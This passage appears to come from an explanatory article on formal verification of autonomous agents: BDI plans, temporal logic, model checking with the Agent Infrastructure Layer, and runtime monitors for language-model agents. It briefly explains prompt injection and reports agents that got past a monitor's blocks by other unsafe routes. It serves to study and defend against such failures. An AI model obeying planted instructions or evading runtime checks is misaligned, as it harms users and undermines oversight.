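# Verifying autonomous agents against safety specifications with intermediate languages and virtual machines

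## Agents, safety rules and the ways of checking one against the other

An autonomous agent is a program that takes in information about its surroundings, decides what to do next and does it without a person approving each step. Formal verification uses mathematical methods to establish whether the agent keeps to a safety specification, which is a precise, machine-checkable statement of what it must never do. One family of methods uses an intermediate language, which sits between the language the agent was written in and the machine that runs it. A virtual machine, which is itself a program, executes the intermediate language one instruction at a time. Researchers first developed this approach for robots, satellites and unmanned aircraft whose decisions follow hand-written plans. In 2025 and 2026, others applied it to agents that run on large language models.

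### Two kinds of agent

Whoever checks ordinary software asks what it does and when it does it. For autonomous software, Fisher, Dennis and Webster (2013), in *Verifying Autonomous Systems*, add the question why it chose one action over another. That question has a usable answer only if the agent's reasons are open to inspection, and the BDI agent (for beliefs, desires and intentions) has this feature by construction. Its beliefs are the information it holds about itself and its surroundings, which may be incomplete or wrong. Its desires are its long-term goals, and its intentions are the goals it is actively pursuing, together with the plans it has committed to. A programmer writes the plans. In the notation that Fisher, Dennis and Webster use, a plan for a robot that carries parcels through a corridor could look like this:

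```
Goal(deliver) : Belief(at_door), Belief(not occupied)
    <- Action(enter_corridor), Action(hand_over), +Belief(delivered)
```

The goal before the colon triggers the plan, the beliefs after the colon are conditions, and the steps follow the arrow. The last step adds a new belief. A "belief" is just an entry in a data store. If the robot drives into the corridor, an engineer can point to the line that caused this and to the entries in the store at that moment.

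A language-model agent has no such line. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a systematic review of 38 studies, defines such an agent as a system in which a large language model selects and sequences tool calls, sub-tasks or robotic actions. A tool call is a structured request, such as "send this text to this address", which the surrounding software carries out. A trained network produces each choice, and the same request may lead to a different choice next time. A user can ask the model to explain an action, but the explanation is another output of the same network and may not match the computation that produced the action.

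These agents are also vulnerable to prompt injection, a weakness that BDI agents mostly lack. An attacker plants instructions in material that the agent will read as data, such as a web page, an e-mail or the result of a tool call. The network receives its instructions and data as one stream of text and does not reliably separate them, so the agent may carry out the planted instructions with its user's permissions.

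A BDI program is a finite text, so a tool can analyse what the program may do, but with a language model, most checks have to be done on the network's output. Dantas and colleagues therefore treat a plan as a finite sequence of actions and check, before, during or after its execution, whether it satisfies a given property.

### Runs and the rules about them

A state consists of the contents of the program's memory at one moment, along with any facts about its surroundings that the rule concerns. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, model an execution, or run, as an infinite sequence of states s0, s1, s2, …, in which each state after s0 results from one indivisible action in the state before. If the program stops, its last state repeats forever. A property is a set of runs, and a program has the property if all its runs belong to the set.

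A safety property requires that some bad thing never happens. Formally, P is a safety property if every run outside P has a finite beginning with no continuation in P. The violation therefore occurs at an identifiable point and cannot be repaired later. A liveness property requires that some good thing eventually happens. Formally, P is a liveness property if every finite beginning has some continuation in P. "The parcel eventually arrives" is a liveness property, since arrival remains possible however long the robot has waited. Someone watching a running agent can thus detect the violation of a safety property when it occurs, but no finite observation can refute a liveness property.

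Alpern and Schneider also proved that every property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. A specification usually needs both because, according to the RWTH Aachen lecture *Safety and Liveness Properties*, a system that does nothing easily fulfils a safety property. For example, a robot that never leaves its charging station will not run anybody over.

Linear temporal logic (LTL) is a notation for such rules. It starts from facts that are true or false in a single state and adds operators that refer to the rest of the run:

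- □p, "always p": p is true now and in every later state.
- ◇p, "eventually p": p is true now or in some later state.
- ○p, "next p": p is true in the state that comes next.
- p U q, "p until q": q becomes true now or later, and p is true in every state before that.

The last operator, "until", is a common source of mistakes. For example, someone might write the requirement that an agent must authenticate itself before it reads any data as "no data access until authentication". An agent that never authenticates and never reads anything does no harm but violates this formula, because "until" also requires authentication to happen eventually. Alpern and Schneider use "until" as their example of a property that is neither pure safety nor pure liveness. A specification writer who wants only the prohibition has to use a weaker formula.

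### Model checking on a small example

Model checking is an algorithmic way to check whether a model of a system satisfies a formula in temporal logic. If it does not, the method returns a counterexample, a run that shows the source of the problem, as Clarke, Emerson and Sifakis explain in their Turing Award lecture, *Model Checking*. The method goes back to 1981 papers by Clarke and Emerson in the United States and Sifakis in France. The search needs no human guidance, but the system must have finitely many states or, as Clarke writes in a separate account of his own work, also titled *Model Checking*, a finite-state abstraction.

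Suppose the delivery robot stands at the corridor door and runs this program:

```
if the corridor is occupied: wait ten seconds
enter the corridor
```

The rule is "never enter the corridor while it is occupied". To keep the example small, we treat finding the corridor free and driving in as one step, so nobody can enter in between. We also assume that the doors lock behind the robot, so nobody can join it inside. The robot then breaks the rule exactly when it reaches a state in which "inside" and "occupied" are both true. In LTL, the rule is □¬(inside ∧ occupied), which means that it is always the case that "inside" and "occupied" are not both true.

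The model is a Kripke structure, a graph of labelled states. *Model Checking* (Cunha, 2017) defines it as a finite set of states, a subset of initial states, a relation that gives every state at least one successor, and a function that labels each state with the facts true in it. Five states are enough to model the robot.

| State | Facts true in it | Next states, first program | Next states, repaired program |
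|---|---|---|---|
| s0 (initial) | at door | s2 | s2 |
| s1 (initial) | at door, occupied | s2 or s3 | s0 or s1 |
| s2 | inside | s4 | s4 |
| s3 | inside, occupied | s4 | s4 |
| s4 | delivered | s4 | s4 |

The checker starts from the initial states, follows every arrow and records the states it has visited. From s0 it reaches s2 and then s4, which leads only back to itself. From s1 it reaches s3, where both facts are true, so it reports the run s1, s3, s4, s4 and so on. In this run, somebody is in the corridor, the robot waits ten seconds, and it then drives in while the person is still there, because the program never checks the corridor a second time.

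Replacing "if" with "while" fixes the program. After each wait the robot is back at the door and looks again, so the arrows from s1 now lead to s0 and to s1 itself. No arrow leads to s3 any more, so a second search visits only s0, s1, s2 and s4, and the rule holds on every run. There are infinitely many runs, since the robot may wait any number of times, but a finite search can cover them because they all stay within these four states.

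The repaired program still does not guarantee a delivery. On the run s1, s1, s1, …, the person never leaves and the robot waits forever, so ◇delivered fails. Proving ◇delivered requires assuming that the corridor eventually clears and that the robot then finds it clear.

The first simplifying assumption is a more serious weakness. On a real robot, looking and driving are probably separate instructions, and somebody could step into the corridor between them. A faithful graph would then have a sixth state, in which the robot has found the corridor free but has not yet moved. One arrow from that state would lead to s3, so the repaired program would fail again. The search was correct for the five-state graph, but the person who drew that graph had merged looking and driving into one step.

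### What each kind of check can conclude

Testing runs the program on selected cases. The first robot program passes a thousand trials if, in each one, the corridor happens to be free or to clear within ten seconds. Testing can therefore prove that a fault exists, but it can't rule out faults in runs that nobody tried. But testing can use the real machine with its real sensors, and Fisher and Dennis, in *Verifiable Autonomy*, typically rely on it for a robot's low-level control, where the environment is too complex for exhaustive analysis.

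Model checking covers all runs of the model, and its conclusion holds for that model. The computation required grows quickly because each additional yes-or-no fact can double the number of states. Twenty independent facts allow more than a million combinations.

In a deductive proof, as Fisher and Dennis describe it, one logical formula describes the system's behaviour, and the prover must show that this formula implies the requirement. The usual way to prove a safety property is to use an invariant, a statement that is true at the start and that no step can make false. For the repaired robot, the invariant is "if the robot is inside, the corridor is free of people". It is true at the start because the robot is outside. The only instruction that puts the robot inside runs after a look has found the corridor free, and the locked doors keep it free. The proof doesn't involve enumerating states,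 so it would also work for a building with any number of corridors, which no exhaustive search could cover directly. However, someone has to find the invariant, which can take considerable skill for a program of realistic size. The proof also depends on the same two assumptions as the graph.

Runtime enforcement covers only the run in progress, not all possible runs. A monitor follows that run and stops any action that would break the rule. (Runtime verification, the milder form, only reports the breach.) The monitor doesn't need to know how the agent reaches its decisions, which makes it attractive for language-model agents, and Dantas and colleagues rate runtime monitoring as the most mature enforcement strategy for them. But a monitor can check only the run so far, and only the actions it sees. Blocking unsafe actions also doesn't ensure that the agent completes its task. In one study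 in their review, on agents that use tools to carry out transactions, blocking 94% of unsafe actions still left fewer than 5% of tasks both safe and correctly completed in most settings, because the agents found other unsafe routes. Dantas and colleagues call for independent replication of that result, so the figures are better read as a warning than as a general rate.

### Steps with a definition: bytecode and the Java Virtual Machine

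The sixth state of the corridor graph leaves a practical problem: somebody has to settle what counts as one step of the agent. Programming languages that run on a virtual machine already come with an answer, and Java is the convenient example. A compiler translates Java source code into bytecodes, the instructions of the Java Virtual Machine. Oracle, in *Chapter 1. Introduction*, of the machine's specification, defines it as an abstract computing machine with its own instruction set and memory areas. (The isolated copies of whole computers that cloud companies rent out share the name "virtual machine" but are a different thing.) Oracle also shows what the compiler makes of a method that adds two whole numbers. The single line `return i + j` becomes four instructions:

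```
iload_1    push the first number onto a stack
iload_2    push the second number
iadd       take both off and push their sum
ireturn    return the sum
```

With the numbers 3 and 4, the stack holds 3, then 3 and 4, then 7. Each instruction has an exact effect on the state, so it is clear where each step begins and ends. If two parts of a program share a variable, one part may act between two instructions of the other. The line of source code does not show this, just as the five-state graph did not show the moment between looking and driving.

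The Java virtual machine can run code from any language that a compiler can translate into its file format, so a tool that checks bytecode can in principle serve several source languages. According to Oracle, a verifier tests each file against a list of static and structural constraints when the program is linked, and the machine attempts to execute only valid files. O'Reilly's copy of *4.10 Verification of class Files*, another part of the specification, explains that this check is needed because the machine has no guarantee that a trustworthy compiler produced the file. The verifier establishes that the code is well formed, but it does not check whether the robot enters an occupied corridor.

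Verification through intermediate languages extends this arrangement to agents by translating the agent into a form in which every step is defined, running it on a machine that controls each step, and checking the steps against the safety specification. For BDI agents, the Agent Infrastructure Layer, a Java toolkit that several agent languages can share, provides this form. The translated agent runs on the virtual machine of Java PathFinder, a model checker that can return to an earlier choice and try the other branch. Java PathFinder searches the program itself, so nobody has to draw the agent's graph by hand. Fisher and Dennis call this program model checking. For a language-model agent, the intermediate language represents only the plan or the tool calls that the network produces, and the virtual machine can block a step before it takes effect.

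## An intermediate language for agent programs: the Agent Infrastructure Layer

Before the Agent Infrastructure Layer (AIL), researchers checked BDI programs by translating them directly into a model checker's input language. In *Verifying Multi-Agent Programs by Model Checking*, Bordini, Fisher and colleagues describe such a method for AgentSpeak, a BDI language whose plans have the same form as the delivery robot's. They built one translator that produces Promela, the modelling language of the model checker Spin, and another that produces Java, which Java PathFinder (JPF) can check.

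### Direct translation from AgentSpeak

Model checking requires finitely many states, but an ordinary AgentSpeak program can accumulate beliefs, messages and intentions without limit. Bordini and colleagues therefore defined AgentSpeak(F), a finite-state version. Before translating a program into Promela, the user sets nine limits, such as the number of beliefs, pending events and stored messages an agent may have at once. If an agent exceeds a limit during the search, an assertion fails and the verification stops, so a limit that is too low does not cause a program to be wrongly reported as verified.

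AgentSpeak(F) also lacks some features of the full language. A belief may contain constants and variables, as in `pos(r1,2,3)`, but not nested structures, as in `at(r1,cell(2,3))`. Goals and negated conditions may not contain variables that have no value yet. Programmers normally use such variables in goals to get a result back, for instance the name of the nearest free corridor. In AgentSpeak(F) they have to store the result as a belief and look it up afterwards.

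Promela does not support strings, so the translator replaces every name with a number. It stores beliefs, events, messages and intentions in channels, which normally carry messages between processes, and it turns the body of each plan into a procedure with a counter for the next step. The Java translation is simpler because Java has objects and ready-made data structures. It doesn't need most of the size limits, but the user still has to keep the structures small.

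Using Java made verification slower. In one case study, a robot searches a five-by-five grid for two pieces of garbage and carries them to a second robot, which burns them. The garbage lies at random positions, and the first robot's arm may fail up to twice before it grips a piece. For one property, Spin examined 333,413 states in about 66 seconds, while JPF examined 236,946 states in almost 19 hours. With the garbage at two fixed positions, Spin took 5 seconds and JPF took 77. The checks also found mistakes. In an earlier version of the program, one plan lacked a condition, so a robot already carrying garbage behaved inconsistently when it passed another piece.

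The main weakness of this method is that each agent language needs its own encoding of beliefs, goals and plans in the checker's state. Five languages and two checkers would require ten translators, and somebody would have to write, debug and trust each one. Dennis, Fisher and colleagues (2011), in *Model checking agent programming languages*, list ten languages for programming such agents. They describe the translation work as tedious and error-prone, and the generated models as very difficult to understand. That difficulty matters when a check fails, because the counterexample is a run of the generated model and an engineer has to trace it back to a plan in the original program.

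### From a language to a toolkit

The obvious remedy is to encode the concepts once, in a common form, and translate every agent language into that form. UKRI's funding record for the project, *Model Checking Agent Programming Languages*, describes an "intermediate agent language" and automatic, provably correct translations into it. The first version of AIL was a language with its own operational semantics, rules defining exactly how each step changes the program's state. It also had its own reasoning cycle, the fixed sequence of steps in which an agent perceives, selects a plan and acts.

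This version proved too inflexible. Dennis and Fisher report in *Programming Verifiable Heterogeneous Agent Systems* that its reasoning cycle, in particular, could not accommodate the features of the major agent languages. They instead turned AIL into a collection of Java classes that represent beliefs, plans, intentions and whole agents, with a library of ready-made rules that operate on them. To support a new agent language, a developer uses these parts to build an interpreter with that language's own reasoning cycle. AIL's developers left the proofs of correctness to later work.

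AIL is therefore an intermediate language in a looser sense than Java bytecode. Nobody writes or reads a text in AIL. An AIL step also has no single meaning, because each interpreter can select, change or add rules. AIL agents share data structures. Beliefs, for example, are normally in the same place in every AIL agent, so a model checker needs only one way to look them up.

### The layers

Checking an agent involves five layers that run on top of one another. The controller in the middle is part of Agent JPF (AJPF), the extension of JPF for agents.

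| Layer | Contents | Connection to the other layers |
|---|---|---|
| Agent program | Initial beliefs, goals and plans in a language such as GOAL | Contains nothing about verification; a parser turns it into AIL data structures |
| AIL interpreter | The rules and reasoning cycle of that language | Runs the agent and provides methods that test for a given belief or goal |
| AJPF controller | The list of agents and the property to be checked | Uses only a fixed set of methods, whatever the agent language |
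| JPF virtual machine | The Java bytecode of the layers above | Treats the agents as ordinary Java code |
| Host Java machine | JPF, itself a Java program | Runs JPF like any other program |

The fixed set of methods is small. Jensen (2015), in *Model Checking AORTA*, lists methods that perform one reasoning step, put the agent to sleep or wake it up, and test whether it has a certain belief or goal. In principle, any Java-based agent platform can implement these methods without using AIL. Dennis and colleagues discuss this option for JACK, a Java framework for BDI agents, but expect that even small programs would take too long to verify fully, because JACK's code lacks AIL's measures for limiting the number of states.

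The controller also determines what counts as one step of an agent. In the Promela translation, a reasoning cycle has four indivisible parts, and Spin tries every order in which the parts of different agents can run. AJPF normally treats a complete cycle as one step and checks the property at the end. Bordini, Dennis and colleagues report in *Automated Verification of Multi-Agent Programs* that this dramatically reduces the number of states, but users must make sure that their properties do not depend on changes within a cycle. A check at the end of a cycle misses any belief that was added and removed during it.

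The layers are not fully separate. JPF does not require every agent to eventually get a turn, so it also explores runs in which one agent executes forever and the others do nothing. To rule these out, an AIL interpreter needs a rule that puts an agent to sleep when it has nothing to do, even if the original language has no such rule. The toolkit also has a "wait for" step, which suspends an intention until the agent holds a particular belief.

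### What an AIL agent consists of

Dennis and colleagues define an AIL agent as a tuple with ten components:

```
⟨ag, B, R, P, i, I, appPlans, In, Out, S⟩

ag        the agent's name
B         its beliefs
R         rules for deriving further facts from them
P         its plan library
i         the current intention
I         all other intentions
appPlans  the plans that are applicable at the moment
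In, Out   received and sent messages
S         the current stage of the reasoning cycle
```

A particular language may add to these components or ignore some of them. A multi-agent system consists of several such tuples and an environment that the user writes in Java.

The tuple has no component for goals. AIL derives an agent's goals from its intentions. Each intention is a stack of rows with four entries. The event is the reason for the row, for example that the agent has committed to a goal. The deed is the next thing to do, such as an action, a change of belief or a commitment to a further goal. The guard is a condition that must hold before the agent carries out the deed, and the unifier assigns values to variables. The deed ε means "no plan yet".

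### Cleaning a room, row by row

Dennis and colleagues illustrate the mechanism with a cleaning agent. In their notation, `!g` is the goal g and `+!g` is the commitment to it. Names with a capital letter are variables, and ⊤ is a condition that is always true. Suppose that the agent has just committed to cleaning but has no plan, so its intention has a single row with the event `+!clean()` and the deed ε. The library contains this plan:

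```
trigger   +!clean()
prefix    ε
guard     dirty(Room)
body      +!goto(Room), +!vacuum(Room)
```

AIL compares the trigger with the event in the top row and the prefix with the deeds at the top of the stack. Both match. It then looks for a value of `Room` that makes the guard true. The agent believes that room1 is dirty, so `Room` becomes room1. From this, AIL computes an "applicable plan", which lists the event, the guards, the deeds, the unifier and the number of rows to drop:

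```
⟨ +!clean(),
  [dirty(Room); ⊤],
  [+!goto(Room); +!vacuum(Room)],
  {Room = room1},
  1 ⟩
```

AIL drops one row and adds one for each deed. Both new rows have the unifier `Room = room1`, so the table omits that entry:

| Row | Deed | Guard | Event behind the deed |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 (top) | +!goto(Room) | dirty(Room) | +!clean() |
| 2 | +!vacuum(Room) | ⊤ | +!clean() |

The agent processes an intention from the top, so it next commits to going to the room. This puts a new row with the event `+!goto(Room)` and the deed ε on the stack. Dennis and Farwer explain in *Gwendolen* that the old row with the deed `+!goto(Room)` stays underneath because the agent will later use it to test whether it has reached the goal.

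Room1 is upstairs and the agent is on the ground floor. A plan for this case has the trigger `+!goto(Room)`, the guard `current_floor(ground) ∧ upstairs(Room)`, and a body with two deeds: go to the stairs, then go to the room. AIL again drops one row, the one with ε, and adds two. The unifier is still the same in every row:

| Row | Deed | Guard | Event behind the deed |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 (top) | +!goto(stairs) | current_floor(ground) ∧ upstairs(Room) | +!goto(Room) |
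| 2 | +!goto(Room) | ⊤ | +!goto(Room) |
| 3 | +!goto(Room) | dirty(Room) | +!clean() |
| 4 | +!vacuum(Room) | ⊤ | +!clean() |

An engineer can read the agent's reasons from this table. The agent is going to the stairs because it has a goal of reaching room1, and it has that goal because it has committed to cleaning.

Some languages, such as 3APL, also let an agent revise deeds it has already planned, and the prefix exists for this purpose. In the earlier example, the intention has two rows. If room1 turns out not to be dirty, a plan with the trigger `+!clean()`, the prefix `+!goto(Room), +!vacuum(Room)` and the guard `¬dirty(Room)` matches both rows. AIL then replaces both rows with one containing the plan's body, `+!find_dirty_room(Room2)`.

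AIL also generates a candidate for carrying on with the top deed if that deed is not ε and its guard holds. In the example, the agent can carry on if it believes that room1 is dirty. If several candidates remain, a selection function picks one. By default it takes the first in the list, but a language or application can replace the function.

The guard `¬dirty(Room)` could mean that the agent believes the room is not dirty, or only that it does not believe the room is dirty. AIL distinguishes between the two, and the difference matters for safety rules. A robot that has not yet looked into a corridor does not believe that the corridor is occupied. If its plan requires only the absence of that belief, it may drive in without looking.

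### Rules and reasoning cycles

The room-cleaning example shows how a plan changes an intention, but each language decides when this happens. Gwendolen, which Dennis and Farwer developed alongside AIL to test it and to give its data structures a default meaning, has a cycle of six stages:

1. Select an intention.
2. Generate the applicable plans.
3. Select one of them and change the intention accordingly.
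4. Carry out the top deed.
5. Perceive the environment.
6. Turn received messages into new intentions.

In this cycle, the agent creates the two-row intention from the example in stage 3, and stage 4 immediately adds the third row for the commitment to `goto(Room)`. A check at the end of the cycle therefore finds three rows.

Each stage consists of one or more rules. Bordini and colleagues, in *Automated Verification of Multi-Agent Programs*, give a simplified version of the rule for adding a belief:

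```
⟨BB, +b : I, S⟩  →  ⟨BB ∪ {b}, I, S'⟩
```

If the top deed is "add belief b", the agent adds b to its belief base BB, removes the deed from the intention I and moves from stage S to stage S'. In Java, a rule's two main methods are `checkPreconditions`, which tests whether the rule applies, and `apply`, which makes the change.

The library often has several rules for the same situation. For example, if an action fails, the basic rule ignores the failure, and the agent continues with its next deed. Another rule records a problem with the goal behind the action, so that a plan can respond to it. Dennis and colleagues expect most languages to handle failure explicitly. A vehicle whose brake command has failed would behave very differently under the two rules, even with the same plans. A verification result therefore applies to the program together with its interpreter's rules.

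### Interpreters for SAAPL and GOAL

SAAPL (Simple Abstract Agent Programming Language) is a small language that condenses typical features of larger ones. When Dennis and Fisher rebuilt its rules with AIL, they found that many rules in the library were too complicated and still specialised towards Gwendolen. For example, the rule for adding a belief also created a new intention in response to it, which SAAPL does not do. They wrote simpler versions, split SAAPL's planning rule into one rule for finding the applicable plans and another for choosing among them, and added a rule for actions other than sending messages. They note that the result is not equivalent to the published definition of SAAPL.

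GOAL was a harder test, since its definition does not use events or intentions. A GOAL agent has a set of beliefs Σ, a set of goals Γ and conditional actions of the form φ ▷ do(a): if φ holds for the current beliefs and goals and the agent is able to do a, it may do a. What the agent is able to do depends on its capabilities, each of which describes how an action changes the beliefs. For the delivery robot, a conditional action might be

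```
B(at_door) ∧ B(corridor_free) ∧ G(delivered)  ▷  do(enter)
```

where B stands for a belief and G for a goal. Dennis and colleagues represent both conditional actions and capabilities as AIL plans. A conditional action becomes a reactive plan, which has no trigger and applies whenever its guard holds. The capability `enter` becomes a plan whose guard says when the robot can enter and whose body contains the physical action and the changes of belief, such as removing `at_door` and adding `inside`.

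To start the capability, the agent adopts a perform goal, which ends as soon as its steps are complete, whereas an achievement goal lasts until the agent believes it has reached the goal. GOAL's own goals are achievement goals, so the developers changed AIL's method for extracting goals from intentions to return only achievement goals. Otherwise, a capability in progress would have appeared in Γ.

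They also needed new rules for selecting plans, including one for capabilities. They say this rule applies only if the top event is a perform goal and at least one plan is applicable. The Java method they print tests for both conditions, but its last line returns "true" for every other kind of event. This may be a mistake in the printed extract, or the agent may only reach this rule with a perform goal at the top. Either way, it shows how easily a rule and its Java version can end up different.

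GOAL's definition also doesn't specify which conditional action the agent chooses if several apply, so the interpreter has to choose. If it always takes the first one, a model checker explores only the runs that this policy allows, and the result may not hold for another GOAL interpreter.

The SAAPL interpreter took about a week to write and debug, and the GOAL interpreter about two weeks. Both languages are small, and the figures come from AIL's own developers, who knew the toolkit best. By 2011, Dennis and colleagues had interpreters for Gwendolen, GOAL, SAAPL and ORWELL, while those for AgentSpeak and 3APL were still under development. The UKRI record lists AgentSpeak, 3APL, MetateM and Jadex as the languages the project set out to study, and none of these had a finished interpreter by then. The evidence for quick adoption therefore covers small languages with a clear formal definition,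 and is weaker for the larger languages that programmers use in practice.

### Systems that mix languages

Since the AJPF controller only needs objects with the right methods, it can run agents written in different languages in the same system. Dennis and Fisher tried this with the Contract Net, a protocol in which a manager offers tasks and other agents bid for them. In their simplified version, the manager contacts agents one at a time, an agent volunteers exactly when it can perform the task, and the manager accepts the first offer. The system had three agents, one each in Gwendolen, SAAPL and GOAL.

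Even this small example required some adjustment because SAAPL plans, unlike Gwendolen plans, cannot respond to a new belief. The SAAPL agent therefore needed a special "react" event whenever a message with new information arrived. Dennis and colleagues later reported that they had verified the mixed system in AJPF and that combining the agents was simple once the interpreters worked. However, all the agents must share one environment, and each interpreter may have its own definition of a belief or a goal. If the definitions differ, "agent 1 believes g" and "agent 2 believes g" are different tests, although they look alike in a specification.

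In *Verifying heterogeneous multi-agent programs*, Doan, Yuan and colleagues instead translate each program into meta-APL, an agent language that can express both the plans and the strategy for choosing among them. They check the result with Maude, a tool that executes systems of rewriting rules. They also prove that their translations of Jason (a practical version of AgentSpeak) and 3APL programs are correct. This is closer to the original plan for AIL, which was a common language with proven translations.

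Jensen, at the Technical University of Denmark, showed that people outside the original team could also extend AIL. He connected it to AORTA, a component that lets an agent reason about roles and obligations in an organisation. For example, if an agent in the role of borrower takes out a book, AORTA records an obligation to return it by a deadline, and records a violation if the agent misses the deadline. This reasoning runs before the agent's ordinary cycle. Jensen used this extension to verify a group of agents that write a scientific paper together.

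### What the layer leaves out

AIL has a data type for maintenance goals, which require an agent to keep something true, such as a battery charge above 20%, but the 2011 version had no rules to support them. A programmer could approximate such a goal with a plan that responds to the belief that the battery is low. Because a safety specification is separate from the agent's own goals, a checker can still test whether the charge always stays above 20% when the agent has no maintenance goal.

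Later descriptions give the same basic structure. In 2015, Jensen described an AIL agent as combining beliefs, rules, goals, plans, intentions and a reasoning cycle, with Gwendolen as the default. In a later keynote paper, Dennis still presented the framework as two parts, the AIL toolkit and the AJPF model checker.

The 2011 version also had incomplete parsers, so a program written for another implementation of GOAL could not simply run on AIL. AJPF could check only a single program on a single machine, so users had to imitate a distributed system within one Java program. The earlier project had developed a method for AgentSpeak that removes parts of a program irrelevant to a given property, but AIL did not have it yet.

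The common layer does not seem to have made checking slower. Dennis and colleagues rewrote the garbage robots in Gwendolen and checked the same property again. AJPF explored 23,655 states in nine hours, compared with 236,946 states in almost 19 hours for the direct translation into Java. JPF had also changed in the meantime, so not all of the improvement can be attributed to the toolkit. Both checks took far longer than the one in Spin, which had taken about a minute.

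## How a safety rule becomes something a machine can check

The AJPF controller can only check a property that someone has written in a form it can evaluate. For BDI agents, that form is LTL with extra operators for beliefs, goals and actions. A language-model agent has no store of beliefs to inspect, so its rules refer to tool calls and the record of earlier events. In both cases, the rule usually starts as an English sentence. A verifier can check whether a program satisfies the formula, but not whether the formula captures the meaning of the original sentence.

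### Formulas about beliefs, goals and actions

AJPF's property language, which Dennis and colleagues define, has five basic formulas. In the table, `ag` is the name of an agent and `f` is a single fact without variables, such as `at_door`:

| Formula | True in a state if |
|---|---|
| B(ag, f) | f follows from the beliefs of ag, according to the test that ag's own language uses |
| G(ag, f) | f is one of ag's goals |
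| A(ag, f) | the last action that changed the environment was f, and ag performed it |
| I(ag, f) | f is one of ag's goals and ag has selected a plan that can achieve it |
| P(f) | f is a percept that currently holds in the environment |

Larger formulas come from four connectives: if p and q are formulas, so are ¬p, p ∨ q, p U q and p R q. The operator U is "until", as in ordinary LTL. R is "release": p R q means that q stays true up to and including the state in which p becomes true, or forever if p never does. "Always", "eventually", "and" and "if … then" are abbreviations built from these operators. There is no "next". (Dennis and colleagues refer to the standard meaning of R, but the definition they print has the two arguments the other way round. Anyone writing a specification should test which order the tool uses, because swapping them produces a different rule.)

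Take the rule that the delivery robot never enters the corridor while it is occupied:

```
□ ¬( A(robot, enter_corridor) ∧ P(occupied) )
```

If we replace P(occupied) with B(robot, occupied), the formula forbids the robot from entering only while it believes somebody is there. A robot with a broken sensor could satisfy that version and still hit someone.

A second rule is that the robot must not hand over a parcel before it has accepted the recipient's code:

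```
B(robot, code_accepted)  R  ¬A(robot, hand_over)
```

The earlier authentication example needed this weaker formula because it also holds if nobody ever shows a code and the robot keeps the parcel.

The third rule is that the robot must stay out if it believes that the porter believes the corridor is closed. This would require B(robot, B(porter, closed)), which the grammar does not allow because the second argument of B has to be a plain fact. Dennis and colleagues deliberately left out such nested beliefs. A programmer can work around this by giving the robot a fact called `porter_thinks_closed`, but AJPF does not connect that fact to the porter agent's belief base.

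### A shallow kind of belief

Dennis and colleagues describe the language as relatively "shallow". To evaluate B(robot, occupied), AJPF calls a method supplied by the robot's interpreter. In AIL, the same method decides whether a plan's guard holds. It searches the belief base and applies the agent's derivation rules, so B(robot, occupied) can be true even when `occupied` is not stored, if a rule derives it from `person_in(corridor)`.

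To evaluate B(robot, occupied), AJPF only searches the robot's belief base for `occupied`. A logic of knowledge would relate an agent's beliefs to all the situations the agent considers possible, whereas AJPF treats B much like any other predicate. If the belief base contains both `occupied` and `corridor_free`, both belief formulas are true, and AJPF reports nothing unless the specification forbids the combination. The formula ¬B(robot, occupied) means only that the search found nothing. This is mostly an advantage for checking a program, because the same lookup also determines what the robot does.

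The action operator can cause more trouble. Suppose someone writes "the robot enters only if it believes the corridor is free" as

```
□ ( A(robot, enter_corridor) → B(robot, corridor_free) )
```

`A(robot, enter_corridor)` remains true until some agent performs another action that changes the environment. If the robot drops the belief `corridor_free` once it is inside, AJPF would report a violation even though the decision to enter was sound. AJPF also evaluates the formula at the end of a reasoning cycle, after a Gwendolen agent has perceived its surroundings again, so the action may be compared with newer beliefs than the ones that led to the decision.

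### Rules about one request and rules about history

For a language-model agent, the software around the model can see each tool call and its arguments. "No refund above 500" is a condition on a single call. "Never send mail after reading a confidential file" is a condition on the order of calls, in LTL □(read_confidential → □¬send_mail). Sending mail may be perfectly acceptable in itself, so a checker that looks at one call at a time cannot enforce this rule. It has to carry some state from one call to the next:

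| Rule | What the checker has to remember |
|---|---|
| No refund above 500 | Nothing |
| No mail after reading a confidential file | Whether such a read has happened |
| At most two transfers | The number of transfers so far |
| One patient per session | The identifier of the first patient |

*Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (2026) presents ContrAgent, which uses finite automata for this purpose. An automaton for the mail rule starts in a state where mail is allowed and moves to another state at the first confidential read. In a small demonstration with four kinds of temporal rule, ContrAgent caught a violating run for each, while a checker without memory caught none. This result follows from the design of the runs, in which each call was legitimate on its own, and doesn't measure how often real agents break such rules.

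One of the four examples also shows how easily a formula drifts from its sentence. The English rule requires a new confirmation before the agent sends anything after reading untrusted content. The printed formula is

```
(¬send U confirm) ∨ □¬send
```

The formula has no term for reading untrusted content. If the user confirms and the agent then reads a malicious web page and sends a message, the formula is satisfied but the English rule is broken. The formula also forbids sending without confirmation when the agent has read nothing untrusted. It would be correct if the monitor started a new evaluation at each untrusted read. Otherwise, the whole formula needs to go inside □(read_untrusted → …).

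The remembered state must also be correct. For the mail rule, someone has to label the confidential files, and every way of reading them has to go through the checker, including a search tool that returns an extract. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) treats reliable records of where data came from as a prerequisite for enforcing history rules.

*LEANGUARD* (2026) keeps such a record in a journal of earlier events. Before each call, it evaluates rules written in Lean, a language in which a computer can check mathematical proofs. A rule might require that the agent has read a record before changing it, or allow a change only once even if the agent retries after an unclear response. If data that a rule needs is missing or malformed, it blocks the call. *LEANGUARD* proves that, for every possible history, the evaluator returns "true" exactly when the history satisfies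 the rule as interpreted in temporal logic. The proof excludes errors in evaluating a rule, but someone could still have written the wrong rule.

### From policy documents to Cedar

Writing rules by hand is slow, and organisations already have policy documents in English. Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, describe a pipeline that translates such documents, together with the agent's prompt and tool descriptions, into Cedar. Cedar is an authorisation language from Amazon Web Services. Its rules permit or forbid a request, and a matching "forbid" overrides any "permit". In simplified form, the two example rules could look like this:

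```
forbid(principal, action, resource)
when { context.tool == "refund" && context.amount > 500 };

forbid(principal, action, resource)
when { context.tool == "send_mail" && context.session.read_confidential };
```

Cedar doesn't store earlier events, so separate code has to compute `read_confidential` from them and pass it in with the request. This means much of the logic for rules that depend on history is outside Cedar.

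The pipeline has four steps:

1. A program generates a schema from the tool descriptions, listing the possible actions and the types of their arguments.
2. A language model, Gemini 3 Pro in the experiments, writes candidate rules.
3. A "hard critic" uses Cedar's own tools to find syntax errors, mismatches with the schema, contradictions, and rules that have no effect.
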